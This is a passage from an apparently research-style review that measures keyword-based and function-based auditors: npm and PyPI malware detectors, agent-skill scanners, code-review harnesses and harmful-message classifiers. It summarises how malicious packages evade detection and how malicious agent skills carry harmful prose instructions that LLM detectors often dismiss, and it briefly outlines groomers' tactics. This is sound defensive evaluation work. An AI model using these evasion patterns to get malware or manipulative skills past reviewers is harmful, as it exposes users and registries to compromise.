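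The checklist version avoided some bad failures. When the Mistral model was trained on one collection, its average score on the others fell to 0.658, while the checklist version scored 0.901. The checklist version requires ten model calls per text, which took between 0.2 and 2.7 seconds on a single graphics card, depending on the model.

For contracts, the questions could come from the act-by-act record: does the clause oblige the consumer to pay, does the payment depend on the consumer leaving, and does the seller still provide the service? A written rule could then replace the learned tree. Girón and colleagues chose a learned tree because hate speech collections use different definitions, but a reviewer who already has a rule doesn't need to learn one from examples.

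### Who is speaking, to whom, and what came before

An auditor can't fill some blanks in the record from the text alone. The request to keep chats from a child's mother might come from an unknown adult or from a sibling planning a surprise, in exactly the same words. An auditor that sees only the text and always gives the same text the same verdict must get one of these cases wrong, however capable the model is.

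Tuzhykov's results show how much the speaker's role can matter even when the wording gives some clue to it:

| Who wrote the harmful message | Miss rate |
|---|---|
| The person doing the harm | 4.9% |
| A victim describing harm that is still going on | 10.1% |
| A third party reporting someone else's ongoing harm | 36.4% |

A platform that relied on this service to pick out reports from bystanders would miss more than a third of them. Tuzhykov didn't test the service's special settings for such reports. In an exploratory run, Tuzhykov told the service where each conversation took place. On helpline conversations, it no longer flagged seven harmful messages it had flagged before, and it flagged one it had previously missed. Flagging fewer messages may suit a helpline where a counsellor is already present, but not a platform that relies on the service to raise the alarm. The service's software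 had also changed between the runs, so this information may not be the only cause of the difference.

Earlier messages matter as well. Sabadin and colleagues cite an analysis by Lorenzo-Dus and colleagues of 24 chat logs between convicted groomers and adults posing as children. The offenders built trust through praise, small talk and questions about daily life, isolated their targets, and tested whether they would comply. Most messages in such a conversation may be harmless by any rule when read on their own. The reviewer therefore has to record acts across the whole conversation and examine how they fit together, which means reading far more private speech, most of it innocent.

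The facts missing from contracts and policies are often about conduct. A clause that says a company "may" share data doesn't show whether it does, and a company can break a promise not to share it. Brackin cites research by Andow and colleagues in which up to 42.4% of Android apps behaved inconsistently with their stated policies. To check a privacy promise, a reviewer needs the app as well as the policy. To find out what "loyalty completion" costs, the reviewer can ask for the final bills of a few members who left early.

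## Lexical and functional auditors measured against each other

The miss rates in earlier sections come from different sets of programs and documents, so they can't show which kind of auditor is better. A detector that misses 10% of crude malware may be weaker than one that misses 30% of well-disguised malware. A fair comparison requires giving every auditor the same items, then changing the wording and the function one at a time.

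### Setting up a fair test

For software, the test could have five steps:

1. Fix each auditor's rules, prompts and thresholds before it receives any test item.
2. Collect harmful and harmless programs and reword all of them with the same tool. Run both versions of each program to confirm that their effects match.
3. Give each harmful program a harmless partner that keeps most of its wording, and run that too.
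4. Give every version to every auditor, several times if its verdicts can vary.
5. Report the miss rate, the false-alarm rate, and the time and money spent per item. Count crashes and timeouts separately.

The harmless programs need rewording too, because otherwise an auditor could get a perfect score by recognising the rewording tool's style.

Comparing verdicts within pairs also shows differences that overall rates don't. On the software grid, the keyword filter has a balanced accuracy of 50%, the same as an auditor that flagged everything would have. But the filter's verdict changes in both pairs where only the wording differs, while the other auditor's verdict never changes. Neither gets both programs right in any pair where only the function differs.

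The published comparisons meet only some of these conditions. Two reword whole sets of programs, but none pairs each harmful program with a closely matched harmless one, as the minimal-edit contrasts did for messages.

### npm packages, most of them undisguised

The largest comparison is by Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* They ran 11 detection tools, some in several versions, on 6,420 malicious and 7,288 popular harmless package versions from npm. These are some of their results, converted to miss rates and false-alarm rates:

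| Detector | Basis for its verdict | Miss rate | False-alarm rate | Seconds per package |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OSSGadget | text patterns | 8% | 79% | 7.9 |
| Packj, code only | list of sensitive functions | 1% | 86% | – |
| Packj, with a sandbox run | sensitive operations, including those seen in the run | 5% | 64% | 17.9 |
| GuardDog | code patterns and data-flow analysis | 10% | 2% | 2.6 |
| GENIE | data-flow analysis | 54% | 0.1% | – |
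| SAP, most accurate version | statistics learned from examples | 16% | 4% | 9.6 |
| SocketAI | language model | 56% | 0.7% | 146.3 |
| IntelGuard | language model with examples of known attacks | 6% | 1% | – |

Functional evidence alone doesn't guarantee a good verdict. Packj raised fewer false alarms when it ran the packages, but it still flagged 64% of the harmless ones because it treats sensitive operations as suspicious regardless of their purpose. GENIE, by contrast, misses packages that steal only one or two pieces of system information, because its rule for such theft requires at least three different pieces to reach the same web connection.

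The two language-model systems differ even more. Both used GPT-4.1 mini, a small OpenAI model, so the difference comes from the procedures around it. SocketAI prompts the model to challenge its own earlier findings, which often makes it drop correct ones, and reads at most 20 files per package. IntelGuard retrieves similar code from past attacks, along with experts' explanations of why that code was harmful, and prompts the model to compare the package's code with these examples.

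Some of these results may be biased towards particular tools. The lead researcher also led the development of IntelGuard. Its knowledge base came from reports on packages in a public database that also supplied part of the test set. The experts who checked the malicious packages looked mainly at places that GuardDog and OSSGadget had flagged, which may have favoured those two.

The test was also easy in one respect, because 80.3% of the malicious packages used no evasion technique. Guo and colleagues attribute this to the lack of mandatory scanning before publication on npm, which leaves attackers little reason to hide. On the 81 packages that check their environment before acting, the detectors' average detection rate was only 39.5%, though the paper's introduction gives 51.7%. A good overall rate can mask a serious weakness, since a detector that caught 95% of undisguised packages and only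 40% of the rest would still catch 84% overall.

The 80.3% figure may also make disguise look rarer than it is, because a test set can include only malware that someone has found, and the best-hidden packages are the least likely to be found.

Learned detectors can also miss malicious code that isn't disguised. One version of SAP caught 87% of the malicious packages from 2021 but only 39% of those from 2023. Attackers had moved to shorter, plainer code, which looked more like the code in harmless packages. In 21% of all the malicious packages, the malicious code was entirely in the installation commands, so a tool that reads only the JavaScript files would miss it.

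### PyPI packages before and after rewording

In their PyPI study, Guo and colleagues used a rewriting tool on both malicious and harmless packages, as a fair test requires. The tool replaced names, encoded text and rearranged the order of the code. The false-alarm rates here are approximate and come from the paper's counts:

| Detector | Miss rate, before → after | False-alarm rate, before → after |
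|---|---|---|
| PyPI's own check | 1% → 3% | 88% → 71% |
| OSSGadget | 12% → 15% | 84% → 84% |
| GuardDog | 6% → 19% | 6% → 2% |
| Hercule (data-flow analysis) | 16% → 17% | 8% → 14% |
| SAP, random-forest version | 22% → 53% | 6% → 15% |
| SocketAI | 12% → 13% | 7% → 19% |
| GPT-4.1 alone | 2% → 1% | 5% → 63% |
| PyGuard (GPT-4.1 with known patterns) | 1% → 1% | 0.1% → 2% |

SAP's recall, the share of malicious packages it caught, fell from 78.05% to 46.88% after a tool rewrote the packages. Guo, Song and colleagues (2026), in *Bridging Expert Reasoning and LLM Detection*, measured almost the same drop with the same tool and explain why. SAP relies on statistics about a package's text, including how random its names look. The tool replaced names with random 32-character strings, which changed those statistics but not the functions the program called.

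PyPI's own check and OSSGadget are lexical, yet rewording barely raised their miss rates, partly because they flag almost everything, harmless or not. They can also still match library calls, whose names rewording doesn't change. A low miss rate after rewording therefore doesn't show that an auditor judges code by its function.

Hercule is better evidence. It traces data through the program using CodeQL, whose library models have gaps. Its miss rate hardly changed, but its false-alarm rate nearly doubled, possibly because obfuscation is one of the five behaviours it looks for. The paper classes Hercule as dynamic but describes it as static analysis, so the PyPI test provides no evidence about sandbox runs. Packj's results on npm are the only direct comparison with a tool that runs packages.

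GPT-4.1 and the smaller GPT-4o-mini were both right about 97% of the time on the original code. After the rewrite, GPT-4.1 missed almost none of the malicious packages but flagged 63% of the harmless ones. GPT-4o-mini, which Guo, Song and colleagues tested on packages rewritten in the same way, missed about 85% of the malicious ones. A likely explanation is that the rewriting removed the clues the models relied on, and that without them GPT-4.1 labelled packages suspicious by default while GPT-4o-mini labelled them harmless.

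Adding examples of known behaviour helped greatly in both studies. PyGuard's errors stayed low after the rewrite, and IntelGuard missed only about 3% of the rewritten malicious packages. However, the developers tested their own systems, and the unaided models are much older than the ones reviewers can use now.

The comparison is also not perfectly matched, because the "before" figures cover up to 4,757 packages and the "after" figures cover 2,069 of them. Small changes may therefore mean nothing. The rewrite also changed more than names, so it is unclear how much renaming alone would worsen the results. Few harmless packages are likely to look like this in everyday use, so 63% is not an estimate of the normal false-alarm rate.

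### Agent skills, with rules and with language models

Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026), in *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, tested six detectors on 886 malicious and 591 harmless agent skills from seven datasets. Four of the detectors are in use at *skill hubs*, the public sites from which people install skills. Two of those can run either with fixed rules alone or with a language model added, which makes a direct comparison possible:

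| Detector | Basis for its verdict | Miss rate | False-alarm rate | Time and model cost per skill |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ClawHub-Mod | rules | 92.6% | 0% | 0.05 s |
| skillscan-security | rules | 14.9% | 50.4% | 25 s |
| skill-scanner | rules | 63.9% | 12.0% | 4 s |
| skill-scanner | rules and Qwen3.6 | 4.9% | 17.8% | 69 s, $0.0004 |
| skillspector | rules | 48.0% | 17.3% | 1 s |
| skillspector | rules and GPT-5.4 | 5.8% | 22.2% | 21 s, $0.16 |
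| AI-Infra-Guard | GPT-5.4 | 13.9% | 8.5% | 110 s, $0.55 |
| skill-vetter | Qwen3.6 | 7.0% | 6.3% | 78 s, $0.001 |
| skill-vetter | GPT-5.4 | 5.4% | 30.8% | 70 s, $0.51 |

The best overall was skill-vetter with Qwen3.6, a model from Alibaba that anyone can download. It missed 7.0% of the malicious skills and wrongly flagged 6.3% of the harmless ones. The best detector in use at a hub was skill-scanner with the same model, which missed 4.9% and wrongly flagged 17.8%. (The ranking uses F1, a score that combines precision with the share of malicious items caught.)

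Adding a language model helped most where the attacks were written in prose. On one dataset of attacks written mainly in ordinary language, skill-scanner caught 7.5% with its rules alone and 96.8% with Qwen3.6 added.

The model's effect on false alarms depended on whether it could remove findings. In skill-scanner, the model can add findings but can't remove the rules' findings, so the false-alarm rate can only stay the same or rise. In skillspector, the model can also remove findings. With Qwen3.6, this cut the false-alarm rate from 17.3% to 7.0%, but the detector then missed 31.3% of the malicious skills.

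Paying more didn't reliably improve the audits. Running skill-vetter on 100,000 skills would cost about $116 with Qwen3.6 and about $50,000 with GPT-5.4, but it flagged almost five times as many harmless skills with GPT-5.4.

The published rates leave out 53 skills on which skillscan-security crashed or timed out. The counts show that all 53 were malicious. If a hub let them through, the detector's miss rate would rise from 14.9% to 20.0%.

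A detector that uses a language model can also give different verdicts on the same skill from one run to the next. Yang and colleagues ran each such detector three times with Qwen3.6. In one set of skills that attackers had published, AI-Infra-Guard gave inconsistent verdicts on 64.3% and skillspector on 57.4%. Overall scores stayed fairly stable because changes in one direction offset changes in the other. A single run is therefore weak evidence about any particular skill.

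That set is unusually hard because all 34 of its harmless skills had once been labeled "malicious". No other set in these studies comes as close to keeping suspicious wording fixed while the function changes.

### Threats that detectors recognised and then dismissed

To find out why detectors flagged harmless skills, Yang and colleagues examined 2,790 of the findings behind those flags. The largest group, 36%, concerned access to passwords, settings or other local data. One detector blocked a phone-call skill because it sent an access key to a web service, but that service had issued the key, so this was an ordinary login.

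Another 10% concerned wording that resembled an attempt to manipulate the agent. One skill included an instruction not to ask permission before "phase 3", which was only the next stage of the task the user had requested. In other cases, the detector flagged a skill because part of it was missing or unreadable, which is a reason to withhold a verdict but not evidence of malice.

When detectors that used only rules missed a harmful skill, they had usually failed to identify the harmful part, either because no rule covered it or because it was in prose. Detectors that used a language model more often identified the harmful part but let the skill through anyway, which accounted for 64% to 90% of their misses, depending on the detector.

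skill-vetter, for example, recognised the threat in 151 of its 177 misses. In 92 of those cases, it dismissed harmful instructions because the skill contained no code to carry them out, although an agent can act on instructions by itself. In another 19, it advised the user to fix the problem before installing the skill but didn't block it. One script changed the source from which the computer would get its future software. skill-vetter noted that this could bring in tampered packages, then passed the skill because the change did no direct harm.

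Blocking every skill that triggers a warning would block many harmless ones. For example, skillscan-security's warning about undeclared network access appeared on 48.3% of malicious skills and 29.3% of harmless ones. A better rule for dismissing warnings would help reviewers more. When a detector finds an unexplained harmful effect, it could be required to either cite evidence that the task needs that effect or send the skill to a person.

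Yang and colleagues tried something similar by rewriting skill-vetter's instructions to address the errors they had found. On 300 fresh skills from one dataset, GPT-5.4's average false alarms fell from 66 to 9 and its misses from 11 to 6. The gains didn't always carry over. On an unfamiliar dataset with 154 malicious skills, Qwen3.6 missed 109 with the old instructions and 114 with the new ones.

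### The same error rates in a real registry

More than half of the skills in that test were malicious. In a real registry, very few are. If π is the share of items that are harmful, s the share of harmful items that a detector catches, and f its false-alarm rate, then

precision = πs / (πs + (1 − π)f).

The large search for malicious skills described earlier confirmed 157 among 98,380, so π is about 0.16%. Combining that figure with the error rates above gives:

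| | skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 | skill-scanner with Qwen3.6 |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious skills caught | about 146 of 157 | about 149 of 157 |
| Harmless skills flagged | about 6,190 | about 17,480 |
| Share of flags that are correct | 2.3% | 0.85% |

The detector at the hub would catch about three more malicious skills and raise more than 11,000 extra false alarms. A person would need about 530 hours to check skill-vetter's flags at five minutes each. Running the model on the whole registry would cost only about $114, so nearly all the expense would come from checking false alarms.

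This illustrative calculation combines two studies, neither of which measured these totals. The count of 157 malicious skills may be too low, because the original search probably missed some, or too high, because Yang and colleagues confirmed only 95 when they rechecked the labels. With a count of 95, skill-vetter's precision would be about 1.4%.

False-alarm rates on ordinary skills could also differ from those in the test, and may well be higher for some detectors. On ClawHub, one of the largest hubs, skillspector advised against installing 45.8% of about 84,560 skills, whereas in the test it flagged 7% to 22% of harmless skills, depending on the model. Unless a large part of ClawHub is malicious, most of those warnings are wrong.

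For half of skill-vetter's flags to be correct, its false-alarm rate would have to fall from 6.3% to about 0.15%. That is difficult but possible. The PyPI detector in *One Detector Fits All* had a false-alarm rate of 0.1%, and slightly more than half of its alarms were correct.

The right threshold also depends on how much there is to check. The same researchers set the detector to a 10% false-alarm rate for a company that used 584 Python packages, because the company prioritized catching attacks. That setting produced 1.24 false alarms a day, but would have produced more than 200 a day on all of PyPI.

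### Cheap checks first

In *staged review*, a quick check examines every item and sends only the ones it flags to a check that needs more time or resources. Guo and colleagues tested this by giving the items OSSGadget flagged to a language model that could look up known patterns of behaviour. False alarms fell from 2,000 to 192, while misses rose only from 244 to 261.

The second stage removed most of the false alarms but couldn't recover any of the 244 malicious packages that OSSGadget had already passed. If the first stage catches a share s₁ of harmful items, and the second catches a share s₂ of the harmful items it receives, then

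overall miss rate = 1 − s₁s₂.

OSSGadget caught 88.4% of the harmful items, and the second stage kept 99.1% of those, so the overall miss rate was 12.4%. Losses build up quickly when the later stages are less accurate. Three stages that each catch 90% of the harmful items they receive will together miss 27%.

The npm study makes it possible to compare different first stages. Guo and colleagues recorded which packages two tools both flagged, and a two-stage review flags exactly those:

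| Arrangement | Miss rate | False-alarm rate | Harmless packages the language model reads |
|---|---|---|---|
| IntelGuard on everything | 6.2% | 1.5% | 100% |
| GuardDog first, then IntelGuard | 13.7% | 0.4% | 2.5% |
| Packj (code only) first, then IntelGuard | 7.3% | 1.3% | 86% |
| GuardDog and IntelGuard on everything, flag if either does | 2.6% | 3.5% | 100% |

Using GuardDog as a first stage filters out nearly all the harmless packages before they reach the language model, but it more than doubles the miss rate. Packj adds few misses, but it passes on so many harmless packages that it barely reduces the language model's workload. A registry with the resources to run both tools on every package gets the lowest miss rate but has more flags to check.

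The two tools also tend to miss the same packages. If their misses were independent, 0.6% of malicious packages would get past both, but 2.6% did, about four times as many. Multiplying the miss rates is therefore likely to overestimate the benefit of adding a second tool.

The malicious packages that a first stage misses are hard to measure. If 1 package in 1,000 is malicious and GuardDog misses a tenth of those, about 1 in 10,000 of the packages it passes will be malicious. A random sample of 1,000 passed packages will usually contain none. It is more practical to run known malicious packages through the first stage in a closed test environment and count how many it passes.

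### Files skipped because of their names

Sometimes the first stage is a line of code that nobody thinks of as an auditor. *Where AI Vulnerability Discovery Harnesses Go Quiet* (Evron, 2026) examines 12 open-source *harnesses*, programs that choose which code to give a language model and process its answers. It identifies 13 kinds of step at which a real flaw can be lost, before or after the model has read the code.

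One of these steps is a keyword filter that saves time by skipping any file whose path contains a word such as "log" or "script". It therefore skips `auth/login.py` and `transcript.go`, because "login" contains "log" and "transcript" contains "script". The model never reads the login file, even though that is one of the most important places to look for security flaws. The chatbot filter that found "harm" in "harmless" made the same mistake, except that here a match makes the auditor ignore an item instead of flagging it.

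If a harness skips files, even a perfect functional auditor will miss the flaws in them. If the skipped files contain 10% of the flaws and the model finds 90% of the rest, the whole system finds 81%. A test that gives all the files directly to the model would still measure 90%.

Size limits can have the same effect. In Yang and colleagues' tests, skill-scanner with a language model failed to identify the harmful part in 66 cases. In 39 of those, the model hadn't received the skill's main instructions because they were too long.

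A report with no findings can mean that the code has no flaws, that the model missed one, or that a flawed file never reached the model. Under Evron's proposed test, a harness has disclosed a skip only if its report, or another output that the documentation tells users about, names the skipped item or gives a count of skipped items that a reader can connect to that item. A smaller total number of files doesn't qualify, and neither does a message that appears only on the screen during the run.

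Evron maintains two of the 12 harnesses and makes no claim about how common these faults are. Developers can prevent or detect them with little effort by matching whole folder names and file types instead of fragments of words, listing every skipped file in the report, and putting a known flaw in a test file called `auth/login.py` to see whether the harness reports it.
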